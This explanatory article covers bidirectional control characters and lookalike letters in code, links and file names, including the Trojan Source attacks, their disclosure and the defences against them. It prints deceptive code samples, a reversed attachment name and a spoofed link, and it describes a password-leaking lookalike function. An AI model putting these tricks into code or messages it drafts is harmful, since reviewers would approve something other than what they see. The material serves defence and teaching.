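# Bidirectional control characters and lookalike letters in code, links and addresses prepared by AI agents

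## How text is stored, ordered and drawn on screen

Unicode is the standard that almost all modern software uses to represent text. A few of its characters change the order in which nearby text appears on screen, and many others look the same as ordinary letters. Either kind can make the text a person sees differ from what the machine processes. Criminals have used this mismatch in email attachments for well over a decade. It now affects AI systems too, because they write emails, commands and payments that people approve from a screen.

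Suppose an AI system has prepared an email with an attachment and is waiting for its user's approval. The screen shows the attachment's name as `March 25 rcs.docx`, which looks like a Word document. The actual name is `March 25 \u{202E}xcod.scr`, where `\u{202E}` stands for a single invisible character that makes the rest of the name appear backwards. The `.scr` extension belongs to Windows screensavers, which are programs that run when somebody opens them. The email is hypothetical, but the file name comes from *Masquerading*, an entry in the catalogue of attack techniques that the American non-profit MITRE maintains.

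The AI system in this story is an agent, a language model that can use tools, for instance to edit files, run commands or send messages. Its email is a draft, which is anything an agent has prepared that takes effect only when a person approves it. Drafts can also be code, commands or payments. The person accepts or refuses the draft on a screen called the approval prompt. An agent can produce a draft like this one without being malicious. It may have copied the name from a web page or an incoming message. It may also have been affected by prompt injection, in which an agent wrongly follows text in a page, file or message as an instruction.

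### Code points, glyphs and fonts

A computer stores text as numbers. Unicode gives each character a number called a code point, written in hexadecimal after "U+". The Latin letter a, for example, is U+0061. Unicode has 1,114,112 code points, and characters occupy 172,808 of them as of version 18.0, according to *Announcing the Unicode Standard, Version 18.0* (2026) from the Unicode Consortium, the non-profit that maintains the standard.

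A person reading text on screen sees glyphs, the shapes drawn for characters. Glyphs come from fonts, and the Unicode Standard doesn't specify them. The Unicode Consortium's *General Structure* explains that a font can map characters to shapes however its designer likes. The Cyrillic letter п has one customary italic shape in Russia and another in Serbia. Many fonts draw the two characters f and i as one joined glyph. Fonts also often draw two different characters identically.

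Homoglyphs are different characters whose glyphs are identical or nearly identical. The standard example is the Latin a (U+0061) and the Cyrillic а (U+0430), which look the same in most fonts. Programs treat them as different numbers, 97 and 1072, so a plain search for `аnna` with a Cyrillic first letter will not find a contact saved as `anna` in Latin letters. The Unicode Consortium uses the term "confusable", which also covers whole strings that people can mistake for one another, and publishes a list of confusables and a method for comparing them.

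The Unicode Consortium tries to avoid duplicates within a script (a set of letters used together, such as Latin or Cyrillic), so French, German and English share a single Y. It keeps letters from different scripts separate even when they look and sound alike. Latin o, Cyrillic o and Greek omicron are three characters with separate numbers, partly because many older encodings already distinguished them and text must stay the same when converted to Unicode and back. Merging lookalikes would also break the conversion between capital and small letters. For example, three different characters look like a capital D with a bar through it, and each has a different small letter.

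The Unicode Consortium guarantees that it will never remove or renumber a character, so any defence has to come from the software that displays or checks the text.

In an older revision of its security report, the Unicode Consortium counts two identifiers as confusable if ordinary users would mix them up at typical sizes and screen resolutions, even if a typographer could tell them apart on close inspection. It also warns that people often overstate the role of lookalikes in spoofing.

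### Why mixed text needs a reordering rule

A file or message stores characters in what the standard calls "logical order", roughly the order in which someone types or speaks them. English is displayed in the same order, from left to right. Hebrew and Arabic run from right to left, so the first stored letter of a Hebrew word appears at its right-hand end. When a single line contains both directions, software needs a rule for where to place each character. Such lines are routine in Arabic and Hebrew, where numbers usually run from left to right and brand names or technical terms often appear in Latin letters.

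The rule is the Unicode Bidirectional Algorithm, which the Unicode Consortium (2026) specifies in a document known as Unicode Standard Annex #9, or UAX #9. It works on one paragraph at a time and starts from a directional type that each character carries:

- Strong characters have a fixed direction. Latin and Cyrillic letters are strong left-to-right characters, and Hebrew and Arabic letters are strong right-to-left ones.
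- Weak characters are mostly digits and the signs that go with them, such as the plus sign, the comma and currency symbols. Their place depends partly on the strong characters before them.
- Neutral characters, such as spaces and quotation marks, have no direction of their own. A neutral between two stretches of text that run the same way joins them. Where the two sides disagree, it follows the direction of the passage it sits in.

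The algorithm uses these types to assign every character an embedding level, a number that records how deeply the text is nested. Even levels run from left to right and odd levels from right to left. In an English paragraph, the English text is level 0, a Hebrew quotation inside it is level 1, and an English word inside that quotation is level 2. The first strong character in a paragraph determines whether its levels start at 0 or 1, unless the software has already set a direction.

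In the last step, the software finds the highest level on the line and reverses every unbroken run of characters at that level. It then moves down one level at a time, each time reversing every unbroken run at that level or higher, and stops after the lowest odd level.

The annex illustrates this with capital letters standing for Hebrew or Arabic ones. If the stored text `car MEANS CAR.` is a right-to-left passage inside an English paragraph, the English word `car` has level 2 and everything else has level 1. Reversing level 2 gives `rac MEANS CAR.`, and then reversing levels 1 and 2 together gives `.RAC SNAEM car`. The English word reads normally because it was reversed twice, while the rest was reversed only once and now runs from right to left, as a Hebrew reader expects.

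This can mislead people even when nobody intends it. One of the annex's examples is the line of code `x + tav == 1`, which checks whether the sum of `x` and `tav` equals 1. If the programmer writes the name `tav` in Hebrew letters, the equals signs and the digit 1 become part of the right-to-left run. An ordinary left-to-right display then shows the line as `x + 1 == VAT` (again with capitals for Hebrew), which reads as a different comparison, although the stored program works as before.

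### The nine controls

The characters' types alone sometimes give the wrong order. For example, if an English sentence quotes a Hebrew book title that ends in the word "java", the algorithm by default treats "java" as part of the English sentence and puts it to the right of the Hebrew, when it belongs on the left. Unicode includes bidirectional control characters to fix such cases. These invisible characters change the displayed order of nearby text without changing the stored order. Nine of them mark the start or end of a stretch of text.

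| Code point | Name | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| U+202A | Left-to-right embedding | Starts a nested passage that runs left to right |
| U+202B | Right-to-left embedding | Starts a nested passage that runs right to left |
| U+202C | Pop directional formatting | Ends the most recent embedding or override still open |
| U+202D | Left-to-right override | Forces the characters that follow to run left to right, whatever their type |
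| U+202E | Right-to-left override | Forces the characters that follow to run right to left, whatever their type |
| U+2066 | Left-to-right isolate | Starts a left-to-right passage that cannot affect the order of the text outside it |
| U+2067 | Right-to-left isolate | Starts a right-to-left passage that cannot affect the order of the text outside it |
| U+2068 | First strong isolate | Starts an isolate that takes its direction from its first strong character |
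| U+2069 | Pop directional isolate | Ends the most recent isolate, and any embedding or override still open inside it |

Isolates are the newer design, and the book title shows why the Unicode Consortium added them. Suppose the sentence continues with the price, `- $19.95 in hardcover`. If the writer wraps the title in a right-to-left embedding, the title displays correctly, but the price appears on the wrong side of it. The reader sees `it is called "$19.95 - "java OT NOITCUDORTNI NA in hardcover.` An isolate keeps the price in the right place. The Consortium now recommends isolates for software that inserts text into a template without knowing the text's direction.

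Embeddings and isolates set the direction of a passage, but letters inside it keep their own direction, so an English word in a right-to-left embedding still reads normally. Overrides replace the letters' own direction, so English text under U+202E runs backwards. Overrides have rare legitimate uses, such as part numbers that mix English letters, digits and Hebrew letters and must run from right to left throughout. The annex advises avoiding overrides wherever possible because of their security problems.

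Three more controls, the left-to-right, right-to-left and Arabic letter marks (U+200E, U+200F and U+061C), each act like an invisible letter with a strong direction. They need no closing character. The effect of all twelve controls stops at the end of the paragraph, which in plain text is usually the line break.

Sorting and searching should ignore bidirectional control characters, according to the Unicode Consortium's *Special Areas and Format Characters*, but text editors have to preserve them because losing one half of a pair can scramble legitimate text. Deleting every control would therefore damage real Hebrew and Arabic text.

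### The file name, step by step

The attachment from the hypothetical email needs only one control, U+202E. With levels marked, it looks like this:

```
stored order:     March 25 \u{202E}xcod.scr
levels:           000000000        11111111
displayed order:  March 25 rcs.docx
```

The first strong character is the Latin M, so the paragraph starts at level 0, and the text before the override stays at that level. The override raises the next eight characters to level 1 and makes the algorithm treat each of them, including the full stop, as a right-to-left letter. Level 1 is both the highest level on the line and the lowest odd one, so the algorithm reverses those characters once, displaying `xcod.scr` as `rcs.docx`. The override has no glyph, so the reader can't see where the reversed text begins.

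Windows opens the file according to the extension at the end of its stored name, `.scr`, without applying this reversal.

The real extension still appears somewhere in the displayed name, here as the `rcs` before the dot. A careful attacker picks a name in which it is hard to notice. In MITRE's other example, the JavaScript file `photo_high_re\u{202E}gnp.js` appears as `photo_high_resj.png`, and a hurried reader could take `resj` for a typo. When the security journalist Brian Krebs tried the method for Krebs on Security's *'Right-to-Left Override' Aids Email Attacks* (2011), a Mac displayed a Windows program as `evilexe.doc`. Attackers sometimes get the trick wrong. The Georgia Straight, a Vancouver newspaper, described a 2015 spam campaign whose attachment had a name ending in `Ind□cod.exe`, with a box in place of the override and the real extension visible.

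Attackers can do only so much with one reversal in a file name, but source code gives them more options. Krebs on Security (2021) reported on Trojan Source, a method in which University of Cambridge researchers used the same control characters to make the code a reviewer sees differ from the code a compiler processes.

### Characters that are merely invisible

People often lump the bidirectional controls together with other characters that have no glyph. Paultendo's blog post *A threat model for Unicode identifier spoofing* gives the example of a username that looks like `admin` but has a zero-width space (U+200B) between the d and the m, so a database treats it as a different name. The zero-width space is meant to mark where a line may break in languages such as Thai and Khmer, which put no visible spaces between words.

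Merely invisible characters and bidirectional controls are easy to tell apart by deleting them and checking whether the display changes. Removing the zero-width space from `admin` leaves it looking the same, but removing the override from the attachment's name changes the displayed name to `March 25 xcod.scr`, because the override was reordering the text on screen. A homoglyph is a visible character in its proper place, but it is the wrong character, so a filter that strips out invisible characters will catch a zero-width space or an override but miss a Cyrillic а.

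Characters that are only invisible have also become a concern for AI, since they can carry text that a model reads and a person doesn't see. Freytag, Davis and Scherer (2026), in *Make sequences with multiple variation selectors in a row formally non-conformant*, listed places where such characters can serve no legitimate purpose and proposed that software show them there as a missing glyph, typically an empty box, citing prompt injection as one reason. Much of their proposal deals with variation selectors, invisible characters that pick between versions of a glyph, such as the plain and emoji forms of a symbol. Unicode 18.0 includes recommendations to make misused variation selectors visible, and the Unicode Consortium's announcement cites research showing that long runs of them can be used to attack AI applications.

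### Three readers of one draft

The person at the approval prompt sees a draft's glyphs in displayed order. The program that acts on the draft, such as a mail client, a compiler or a bank's payment system, processes its code points in stored order. The model also receives the stored text, not the on-screen rendering, unless someone gives it a screenshot. So the model and the program can both process `March 25 \u{202E}xcod.scr` while the person sees `March 25 rcs.docx` and approves what looks like a Word document.

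A control character in a draft can change the direction of the text around it, including the text of the approval prompt. The Georgia Straight describes this happening to a Mac OS X security warning. The system warned the user about a malicious file with an override in its name, but the override made the warning run from right to left, so it was hard to read.

The Japanese messaging app +Message handled a similar problem better. *URL Spoofing Using RTLO in Messaging Apps* describes a message containing `\u{202E}https://evil.akaki.io/#moc.elgoog`, which the app displayed as a link beginning with `google.com` but which opened `evil.akaki.io` when tapped. The developers added a warning that appears before such a link opens and shows the address unreversed, so the user can see where the link leads. This fix would not help against a Cyrillic а substituted for a Latin a, because that address already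 appears in its stored order.

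## Trojan Source: code that a compiler reads in another order

A compiler turns source code into something a computer can run, and it reads the characters in the order they are stored. In *Trojan Source*, Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson of the University of Cambridge used bidirectional control characters to write programs that looked harmless on screen but did something else when they ran. The paper was released on 1 November 2021 and appeared at the USENIX Security conference in 2023.

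The idea grew out of machine-learning experiments, according to *Trojan Source*, the Light Blue Touchpaper blog post that announced the paper. The researchers had already used the same control characters, along with homoglyphs, to break translation systems and toxic-content filters.

The attack has the number CVE-2021-42574 in CVE, a public list of software vulnerabilities. Ubuntu's *CVE-2021-42574* (2021) gives it a severity score of 8.3 out of 10. The entry places the flaw in Unicode's Bidirectional Algorithm, and the Unicode Consortium objected to that wording.

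Many open-source projects accept code from strangers and rely on human reviewers to catch anything malicious. Boucher and Anderson assume an attacker who can submit a change to such a project or to a library it depends on. The attacker can also post a code sample online for others to copy, because most browsers, editors and operating systems preserve bidirectional control characters through copy and paste. An agent that copies code from a web page could introduce the characters in the same way.

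### Why comments and strings are the opening

A compiler first splits the code into tokens, such as names, numbers, operators and brackets. It doesn't run the bidirectional algorithm. It usually stops with an error if it finds a control character between two tokens, so an attacker can't put these characters just anywhere in a program.

Compilers accept nearly any character, including bidirectional control characters, inside comments and string literals. Comments are notes for human readers, and the compiler skips them. String literals are pieces of text in quotation marks, such as a message the program will print, and the compiler keeps their contents unchanged.

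In C, a comment that starts with `/*` ends at the next `*/`, but the bidirectional algorithm does not treat those symbols as boundaries. A control left unclosed in a comment therefore keeps working until the end of the line. It can make code that follows the comment appear in a different place, or make part of the comment appear outside it. Red Hat (2022), whose engineers worked on a defence for the C compiler GCC, traced the problem to this mismatch between the algorithm's rules for lines and paragraphs and the language's rules for comments and strings.

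Most reorderings would produce gibberish that any reviewer would question. Boucher and Anderson's main insight was that an attacker can choose one where the displayed text is also valid code. They describe this as turning one program into an anagram of another.

Isolates make this reordering practical because the algorithm moves each isolate as a single block. The examples below use the standard abbreviations RLI and LRI for the controls that start a right-to-left and a left-to-right isolate, PDI for the control that ends an isolate, and RLO for the right-to-left override. The stored sequence `RLI LRI abc PDI LRI def PDI PDI` appears on screen as `defabc`. The two blocks swap places, but the letters within each still read normally. By nesting more isolates, an attacker can display the pieces of a line in almost any order.

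### Early return: the bank withdrawal

The first form of attack in the paper is the early return, in which the attacker hides a working `return` in what looks like a comment. A `return` ends a function, so nothing after it in that function runs.

The published Python example has a bank in which Alice has 100, and a function that subtracts money from an account. On screen, the first line inside the function looks like this:

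```
''' Subtract funds from bank account then return; '''
```

The line in triple quotation marks is a docstring, a description that Python programmers conventionally put at the top of a function. It appears to describe a function that subtracts the money and then returns. The next line subtracts the money. If the program withdraws 50, a reviewer expects Alice to have 50 left.

She still has 100. The docstring line contains a single control:

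```
stored order:     ''' Subtract funds from bank account then [RLI]''' ;return
displayed order:  ''' Subtract funds from bank account then return; '''
```

The closing quotation marks come straight after the control character, so the docstring ends there. After the semicolon, Python runs `return` as a second statement on the same line, so the function stops before it reaches the subtraction.

The screen shows a different order because RLI starts a right-to-left passage at level 1. The closing quotation marks, the space and the semicolon have no direction of their own, so they take level 1. The Latin letters of `return` get level 2. The algorithm first reverses `return`, then the whole passage, which leaves the word readable but moves it to the left of the quotation marks.

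The same trick is clumsier in C, because reversing the closing `*/` turns it into `/*`. Boucher and Anderson avoided this by using `/*/`, which works in both directions but looks odd to an experienced programmer.

### Commenting out and stretched strings

Commenting out works the other way round: text that looks like code is really part of a comment, so it never runs. This lets an attacker remove a security check while leaving it visible. In the paper's C example, the program sets `isAdmin` to false and then appears to print "You are an admin." only if `isAdmin` is true. Red Hat printed the code points of the important line, which are these:

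```
stored order:     /*[RLO] } [LRI]if (isAdmin)[PDI] [LRI] begin admins only */
displayed order:  /* begin admins only */ if (isAdmin) {
```

In stored order, the whole line lies between `/*` and `*/`, so the compiler skips it, including the check, and the program prints its message to everybody. On screen, the override moves the second isolate to the left and the first to the right, so the comment seems to close before `if (isAdmin)`. The brace also looks correct, because Unicode mirrors brackets in right-to-left text and the stored `}` appears as `{`.

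The mirroring also affects `<` and `>`, which programs use to compare numbers, so a reversed comparison can look perfectly ordinary.

A stretched string is a string literal that contains more than it seems to. Rust Security Response WG's *Security advisory for rustc (CVE-2021-42574)* (2021) gives an example in the language Rust, where `!=` means "is not equal to":

```
stored order:     if access_level != "user[RLO] [LRI]// Check if admin[PDI] [LRI]" {
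displayed order:  if access_level != "user" { // Check if admin
```

A reviewer sees a comparison with the word "user", followed by a comment, but the compiler reads a comparison with a much longer string that includes the supposed comment and the control characters. An ordinary user's access level is `user`, which doesn't equal the longer string, so the program treats that person as an administrator.

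Boucher and Anderson acknowledge that an attacker can make a comparison fail more simply, with a zero-width space or a homoglyph. They also describe functions whose names differ only by a lookalike letter. This problem has its own identifier, CVE-2021-42694.

### Languages and editors

The researchers tried the attack in 12 languages: C, C++, C#, JavaScript, Java, Rust, Go, Python, SQL, Bash, Assembly and Solidity. Each test program looked as if it would print nothing, yet it printed "You are an admin." All three forms of the attack worked in every language, although some combinations needed code in an unusual style. The attack also worked in two other text encodings, one Chinese and one Israeli, so it doesn't depend on the usual Unicode encoding.

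Only Solidity, a language for programs that run on the Ethereum blockchain, had a partial defence beforehand. Its compiler rejected embeddings and overrides but accepted isolates, which were enough for the attack. C# was unusually permissive in allowing controls inside variable names. It ignored them, so a name with a control and the same name without one referred to the same variable.

In October 2021 the researchers also checked how editors and code-hosting websites displayed the programs, on Windows, macOS and Ubuntu. Visual Studio Code and Atom showed the deceptive version on all three systems. So did GitHub, GitLab and Bitbucket in Chrome, Firefox and Edge, while Apple's Safari browser put the text in the wrong order. Some editors already gave the trick away:

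- IntelliJ displayed the control characters.
- Sublime Text didn't reorder the text.
- Vim showed the controls as code points on macOS and Ubuntu, and garbled the text on Windows.

Most editors colour comments differently from code, which can expose the attack. A commenter on Krebs on Security's report opened the examples in Visual Studio Code and found that the colours marked the real comments every time. Boucher and Anderson had more mixed results, with odd colours in some editors for some attacks. They doubt that most developers would notice, and an attacker can test the disguised code in the target's editor first. The cursor also jumps around when someone moves through an affected line with the arrow keys, but reviewers of long changes seldom go through them one character at a time.

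### The 99-day embargo

Boucher and Anderson sent the first reports on 25 July 2021 and gave the recipients 99 days to prepare defences before publication. They contacted 19 companies and organisations. All confirmed receipt, and nine eventually committed to releasing a patch.

Some of the others quickly dismissed the report or pointed to their legal policies. Recipients tended to close a report at once if the problem didn't resemble a familiar kind of vulnerability. The researchers made more progress when they named the specific product at risk. Eleven recipients ran programmes that pay for vulnerability reports, and five of them paid an average of $2,246.

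In September the researchers brought in CERT/CC, a US government-sponsored coordination centre, which added three more vendors and gave everybody a shared place to discuss fixes. In October the researchers alerted the security teams of 21 operating systems. Two recipients experimented with the attack in public repositories before the embargo ended.

The researchers later studied the disclosure process. Light Blue Touchpaper's *Talking Trojan* (2022) warns that the incentives of commercial bounty programmes can clash with those of platforms where many vendors work together on one problem. The number of fixes grew after publication, and Boucher (2024), in *Deception and defense from machine learning to supply chains*, credits the disclosure with patches to dozens of compilers, editors and code repositories.

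Part of the delay came from a disagreement about who should fix the problem. Some developers thought that a compiler should only compile, and that separate checking tools or editors should look for suspicious text. The Java team called it a matter for editors. A guidance document posted to a Python mailing list took a similar position, because a fix in the language itself would restrict programmers too much. Boucher and Anderson replied that compilers already warn about other dangerous practices, and that a compiler check protects everyone who builds the code, whichever editor they use.

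The case for a compiler check is good, since an editor's warning protects only the people who use that editor. But a compiler check does nothing for languages whose maintainers decline to add one, and it runs after the code has been reviewed. GCC's developers made a sensible compromise when they wrote "This is not a compiler bug" in *Bug 103026* but added a warning anyway.

### The defences and their default settings

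The simplest rule is to ban every bidirectional control from source code. A program that needs one in its output can use an escape, a visible code that produces the character when the program runs. But the ban would also reject legitimate Hebrew or Arabic comments that use them, so Boucher and Anderson prefer a narrower rule that rejects only controls left open at the end of a comment or string. Closed controls can still reorder text inside a comment, but they can't move it into the code.

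| Tool | What it does with these controls | On by default |
|---|---|---|
| Rust, from version 1.56.1 | Stops compilation if a string or comment contains one | Yes |
| GCC, from version 12 | Warns about unclosed controls and still compiles | Yes |
| Clang, another C compiler | No warning from the compiler; the separate tool clang-tidy can check | No |
| GitHub | Shows a warning banner | Yes |
| Visual Studio Code | Highlights the characters | Yes |

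Rust is the strictest of these. Its developers received the report on the first day of the embargo and released the new version on the last day. The error message includes an escape sequence for anyone who has a legitimate use for the character. Older versions lack the check. Debian's page on the flaw, *CVE-2021-42574*, lists the Rust 1.48 compiler in the "bullseye" release as vulnerable and later releases as fixed.

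GCC's warning also has a stricter setting that reports every bidirectional control, closed or not. When one of the Red Hat engineers tried an early version on the Cambridge examples, the warnings were hard to understand because they reproduced the disguised lines. GCC now prints the control characters in such warnings as codes, for example `<U+202E>`, so the line appears in stored order.

GitHub's warning banner first appeared on 31 October 2021, the day before Trojan Source was published. Arnold (2021), in *Re*, copied the banner's text into a message to a security mailing list. The banner warned that the file "may be interpreted or compiled differently than what appears below" and recommended opening it in an editor that reveals hidden characters. GitHub's *Warning about bidirectional Unicode text* (2021) told users that they could ignore the banner if the characters were intentional. In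 May 2025, GitHub (2025) announced a warning for hidden Unicode text more generally. One reason it gave was that AI may interpret such text differently from how it appears.

Bitbucket displays the controls as code points. Its owner, Atlassian, says that hovering over one shows a message that such characters could hide malicious code. GitLab also made the controls visible.

Python and JavaScript programmers can get similar protection from linters, programs that check code for mistakes and bad style. Pylint's *bidirectional-unicode / E2502* describes an error message for Python files. For JavaScript, *Detects trojan source attacks that employ unicode bidi attacks* documents a rule that gives a warning in its plugin's recommended configuration. These default settings help only teams that install and run the tools.

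The checks also have gaps. Astral's *bidirectional-unicode (PLE2502)*, the description of a rule in another Python linter, shows one that the most common check would miss:

```
stored order:     example = "x[RLM]" * 100  #    "[RLM]x" is assigned
displayed order:  example = "x"    #  100 * "x" is assigned
```

In Python, `#` starts a comment, so a reader sees a variable that contains one x, but the program repeats the string 100 times. RLM is the right-to-left mark, which never needs closing, so a search for unclosed controls won't find it. It is also not among the nine code points that the Rust advisory recommends searching for.

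After publication, open-source contributors exposed another gap when they suggested putting an ordinary invisible character between the `*` and the `/` that close a comment. The comment looks closed, but the compiler treats the lines after it as part of the comment. This attack does not reorder text, so a check for bidirectional controls will not detect it.

### Searches for real attacks

Before publication, the researchers looked for signs that somebody had already used the method. GitHub searched more than a billion public commits (saved changes to code) from January to mid-October 2021 on their behalf. The search matched 7,444 commits with unclosed controls in comments and strings.

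About 98.8% of the matches were false alarms. Many came from Hebrew or Arabic text with badly formed controls, or from software that had put controls at the start of file paths. The rest included some JavaScript programs that used the controls to obscure their code, which isn't necessarily malicious, and tools for disguising file extensions. The search also found the two recipients who had broken the embargo.

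One match was Slither, a tool that checks Solidity programs for security problems, which already looked for the right-to-left override. Its documentation included an example in which the override swapped two single-letter values on screen, so at least one group of developers had anticipated part of the attack. Go's developers had also discussed something close to a stretched string in 2017, but the discussion did not lead to a fix.

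The Rust team searched every version of every package ever published on crates.io, the language's public package registry. Only five packages contained bidirectional control characters, and none used them maliciously.

These searches are good evidence that the attack was rare or unused in public code before November 2021. They can't rule out its use in private code, and they don't cover the years after the paper made the method public. *Trojan Source Detector* (Weinzierl, 2025) is a set of scripts written for a bachelor's thesis to run a newer search of GitHub. The scripts look for unbalanced controls, invisible characters and lookalike function names, but the project's description gives no results.

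### Reviewing an agent's patch

When an agent fixes a bug and its user must approve the patch (a set of changes to existing code), the user's protection depends on where they view it.

In a web diff, a page that shows the old and new lines together, the most likely defence is GitHub's warning. It leaves the decision to the reviewer, whom GitHub advises to continue in an editor. Other websites need their own warnings. In November 2021, *Add warnings when displaying code with bidirectional Unicode text* (Gerbet, 2021) requested one for the diffs and file pages of Tuleap, another code-hosting tool. An agent product that displays its own diff has no such warning unless its developers build one.

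Projects can add an automatic check, such as the one Altfield (2021) wrote, which scans each change submitted on GitHub and posts a comment if the change contains any character outside basic English text. It also catches lookalike letters, which GitHub's original banner did not. The check would work well for a project written entirely in English, but a project with Arabic or Hebrew text would get constant warnings.

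Visual Studio Code highlights suspicious characters where they appear, so the reviewer can see which line to examine.

The terminal, a text-only window for typing commands, is the least predictable of the three because only some terminals reorder bidirectional text. Wilk (2021), in *Re*, quoted a change to the Rust compiler that removes these controls from the code shown in its messages because command-line programs handle them inconsistently. That makes the compiler's messages safer to read, but it doesn't affect a patch that the agent prints directly to the terminal.

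The risk extends to commands. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026), a paper on securing coding agents, warns that a person approving an administrator command could authorise a different command from the one shown on screen.

Compiler warnings may also come too late, because the user can approve a patch before anyone builds the program. If the agent runs the build, GCC's warning goes into the agent's output, which the user may never read. Rust, by contrast, stops the build. Python has no comparable check, so a user who approves a patch like the bank withdrawal in a terminal, in a project without a linter, may get no warning.

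## Lookalike letters in code: CVE-2021-42694 and the curl test

CVE-2021-42694 covers the lookalike function names in the Trojan Source paper. The attacker replaces one letter of a name with a homoglyph, without changing the order of the text, so that a call reaches the wrong function. Swapped letters also work in web addresses, and in 2025 a contributor to the software project curl got one past its reviewers and automated checks.

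### Two functions with one visible name

Boucher and Anderson demonstrate the attack with a C++ program that has two greeting functions. One has a Latin H (U+0048) in its name, and the other has the Cyrillic letter Н (U+041D), written here as a code:

```
stored name         what the function prints
sayHello            Hello, World!
say\u{041D}ello     Goodbye, World!
```

On screen, both names appear as `sayHello`. The compiler compares names by code point, so it treats them as two separate functions. The program calls the one with the Cyrillic letter and prints "Goodbye, World!", although a reader would expect "Hello, World!".

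The paper's more harmful example is a function called `hashPassword`, which scrambles a password so that a website doesn't have to store the original. An attacker could add a lookalike `hashPassword` to a library that the website uses. The lookalike calls the real function and returns the correct result, but it also sends the unscrambled password to the attacker. The website still works, and a test that checks only the result will pass.

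The attacker must add the lookalike function and also get a call with the wrong letter into the website's own code. Otherwise, a developer who types `hashPassword` on an ordinary keyboard still calls the real function.

The same trick works on variables. Müller gives an example on the blog of SemanticDiff, a tool for comparing versions of code. The code appears to replace the value of a variable called `password` with its hash (the scrambled version). But the variable name that the hash is assigned to contains a Cyrillic а, so the hash goes into a new variable that the program never uses again.

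### What compilers and editors do with such names

Boucher and Anderson first tried putting invisible characters in function names, but almost every compiler rejected them. They then tried homoglyphs, which worked in 10 of the 12 languages they tested.

| Language | Result with a lookalike function name |
|---|---|
| C#, JavaScript, Java, Go, Python, SQL, Bash | The program runs and calls the lookalike |
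| C and C++ | The same with the Clang compiler; an error with the tested version of GCC (7.6.0) |
| Rust | The program compiles, but the compiler warns about the name |
| Assembly, Solidity | The attack did not work |

The Rust compiler warns that the name uses "mixed script confusables" and suggests checking that the programmer wants that function. Trojan Source's *Some Vulnerabilities are Invisible* recommends that other compilers add an error or warning for such names.

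A check for mixed scripts within a name can still miss lookalikes. *Unicode-related Security Considerations for Python* (Viktorin, 2021) lists four different names that all look like `scope`: one entirely Latin, one with a Cyrillic о, one with a Greek ο, and one entirely Cyrillic. The check would accept the all-Cyrillic name because it doesn't mix scripts.

Python normalizes names using a standard Unicode method called NFKC, which converts different versions of the same letter to a single form. If a programmer writes `xⁿ = 8` with a raised n, Python sets the ordinary variable `xn` to 8. But NFKC does not merge letters from different scripts, so the four versions of `scope` remain separate names.

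Normalization gives attackers another option because it treats some names that look different as the same. Veracode's *Malicious Actors Use Unicode Support in Python to Evade Detection* describes code that spells the common Python name `self` in mixed bold and italic mathematical letters. Python converts them to plain `self` and runs the code normally, but a scanner that searches for the plain spelling would miss the altered version.

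When Boucher and Anderson tested code editors and repository websites in October 2021, most displayed the lookalike function with no visible sign of the substitution. These included GitHub, GitLab and Bitbucket, as well as IntelliJ and Sublime Text, which had exposed the reordering attack. The only exceptions were Eclipse and Vim on Windows, which failed to draw the Cyrillic letter properly.

Visual Studio Code now highlights potential homoglyphs by default. Boucher and Anderson report that GitLab marks them too, but Müller tried GitHub, GitLab and Bitbucket and got no warning from any. A team that relies on one of these sites for warnings should first test it with a lookalike letter.

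### The swapped letter in curl

curl is a widely used program and code library for transferring data to and from web addresses. Stenberg (2025), in *Detecting malicious Unicode*, describes a test that the contributor James Fuller carried out on the project, which Stenberg leads. Fuller submitted a large clean-up of a set of scripts. In one web address, he had replaced an ASCII letter with a lookalike. (ASCII is the basic set of 128 characters that includes the unaccented Latin letters, the digits and common punctuation.)

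None of the human reviewers commented on the letter, and none of curl's CI jobs, the automated checks the project runs on proposed changes, flagged it. Fuller revealed the swap later in a presentation.

Stenberg reproduced a similar case to show what a reviewer sees on GitHub. He replaced the g in a web address with the Armenian letter co (U+0581), which looked identical. GitHub's diff viewer marked a difference, but a person could not see what had changed. Stenberg adds that a competent attacker would combine the swap with a real and expected fix, so the reviewer would have an innocent explanation for the marked line.

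For comparison, Stenberg used a screenshot from Viktor Szakats of Gitea, another code-hosting tool. Gitea warned that the new line contained "ambiguous Unicode characters". Stenberg would have liked more detail but said the warning would be enough to make him download the code and investigate before accepting it.

Stenberg had also reported the problem to GitHub and received hardly any response. When a reader mentioned GitHub's warning about hidden Unicode text, then two weeks old, Stenberg replied that it didn't help here, since a lookalike letter is not hidden. He published his post on the morning of 16 May, and at 17:30 he added that GitHub was now treating the matter as a security issue and working on a fix. The post has no later update about the fix.

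The developers of OneDev, a smaller code-hosting tool, changed their code in response to the same post. The user daniel-developer had asked them for a warning like Gitea's in a request titled *Detecting malicious unicode in merge requests*, which they closed after making the change.

Fuller's test showed that a lookalike letter can get past an experienced team and its automated checks. It doesn't show how often this would happen, because it covered one letter in one change, and Stenberg doesn't say how many people reviewed it. Fuller was also an existing contributor, and reviewers may look harder at a stranger's work. The test also didn't show how much damage the swap could have done, which depends on what the script does with the address and whether an attacker can register the lookalike domain.

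The test's conditions are common, however. People often give coding agents large clean-ups to do, and often review the result in the same kind of diff.

### Why strings are easier to tamper with

If an attacker only replaces one letter in a function call with a lookalike, the code won't compile because no function has that name. Python raises an error only when it reaches the line, but any test that runs the line will fail. The attacker therefore has to add a function with the lookalike name, and a reviewer may ask why the project needs it. Müller's example avoids this problem in languages such as Python, which create a variable the first time a program assigns a value to it.

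A web address in quotation marks doesn't have to match anything else in the code, so the compiler accepts any letters there. A lookalike letter has no effect until the program uses the address.

Many tests never contact the real address, because they use a local stand-in for the website to avoid failing when the real site is down. Maintenance scripts and links in documentation may have no tests. Even a test that contacts the address could pass if the attacker owns the lookalike domain and serves a copy of the expected file.

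Some strings are riskier for an attacker to change. If a program checks whether a user's role is `"admin"` and one letter in that string is Cyrillic, the check will fail for real administrators. An ordinary test of the login would probably reveal the failure.

A rule about names alone is not enough, as Solidity shows. *Targeting the Weakest Link* (2021), a paper on deceptive programs for the Ethereum blockchain, notes that Solidity bans Unicode symbols in the names of functions and variables but allows them in strings, which can decide which function in another program gets called. In one of the paper's attacks, a homoglyph in such a string makes the program call a function that doesn't exist. The call fails, and the blockchain reverses the whole transaction. The paper places this trap in a function called `sellTokens`, so an attempt to sell the tokens would fail even though the code looks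 correct.

### The check that curl added

curl's answer was to ban almost all characters outside ASCII. The check is part of a script by Szakats that examines every file in the project.

UTF-8, the usual way of storing Unicode text, stores each ASCII character as one byte with a value from 0 to 127, and every other character as two or more bytes with values of 128 or higher. So the script only has to look for a byte in the higher range. If it finds one, the check fails and prints the file name, the line number and the bytes. For the Armenian letter in Stenberg's example, the bytes would be `d6 81`.

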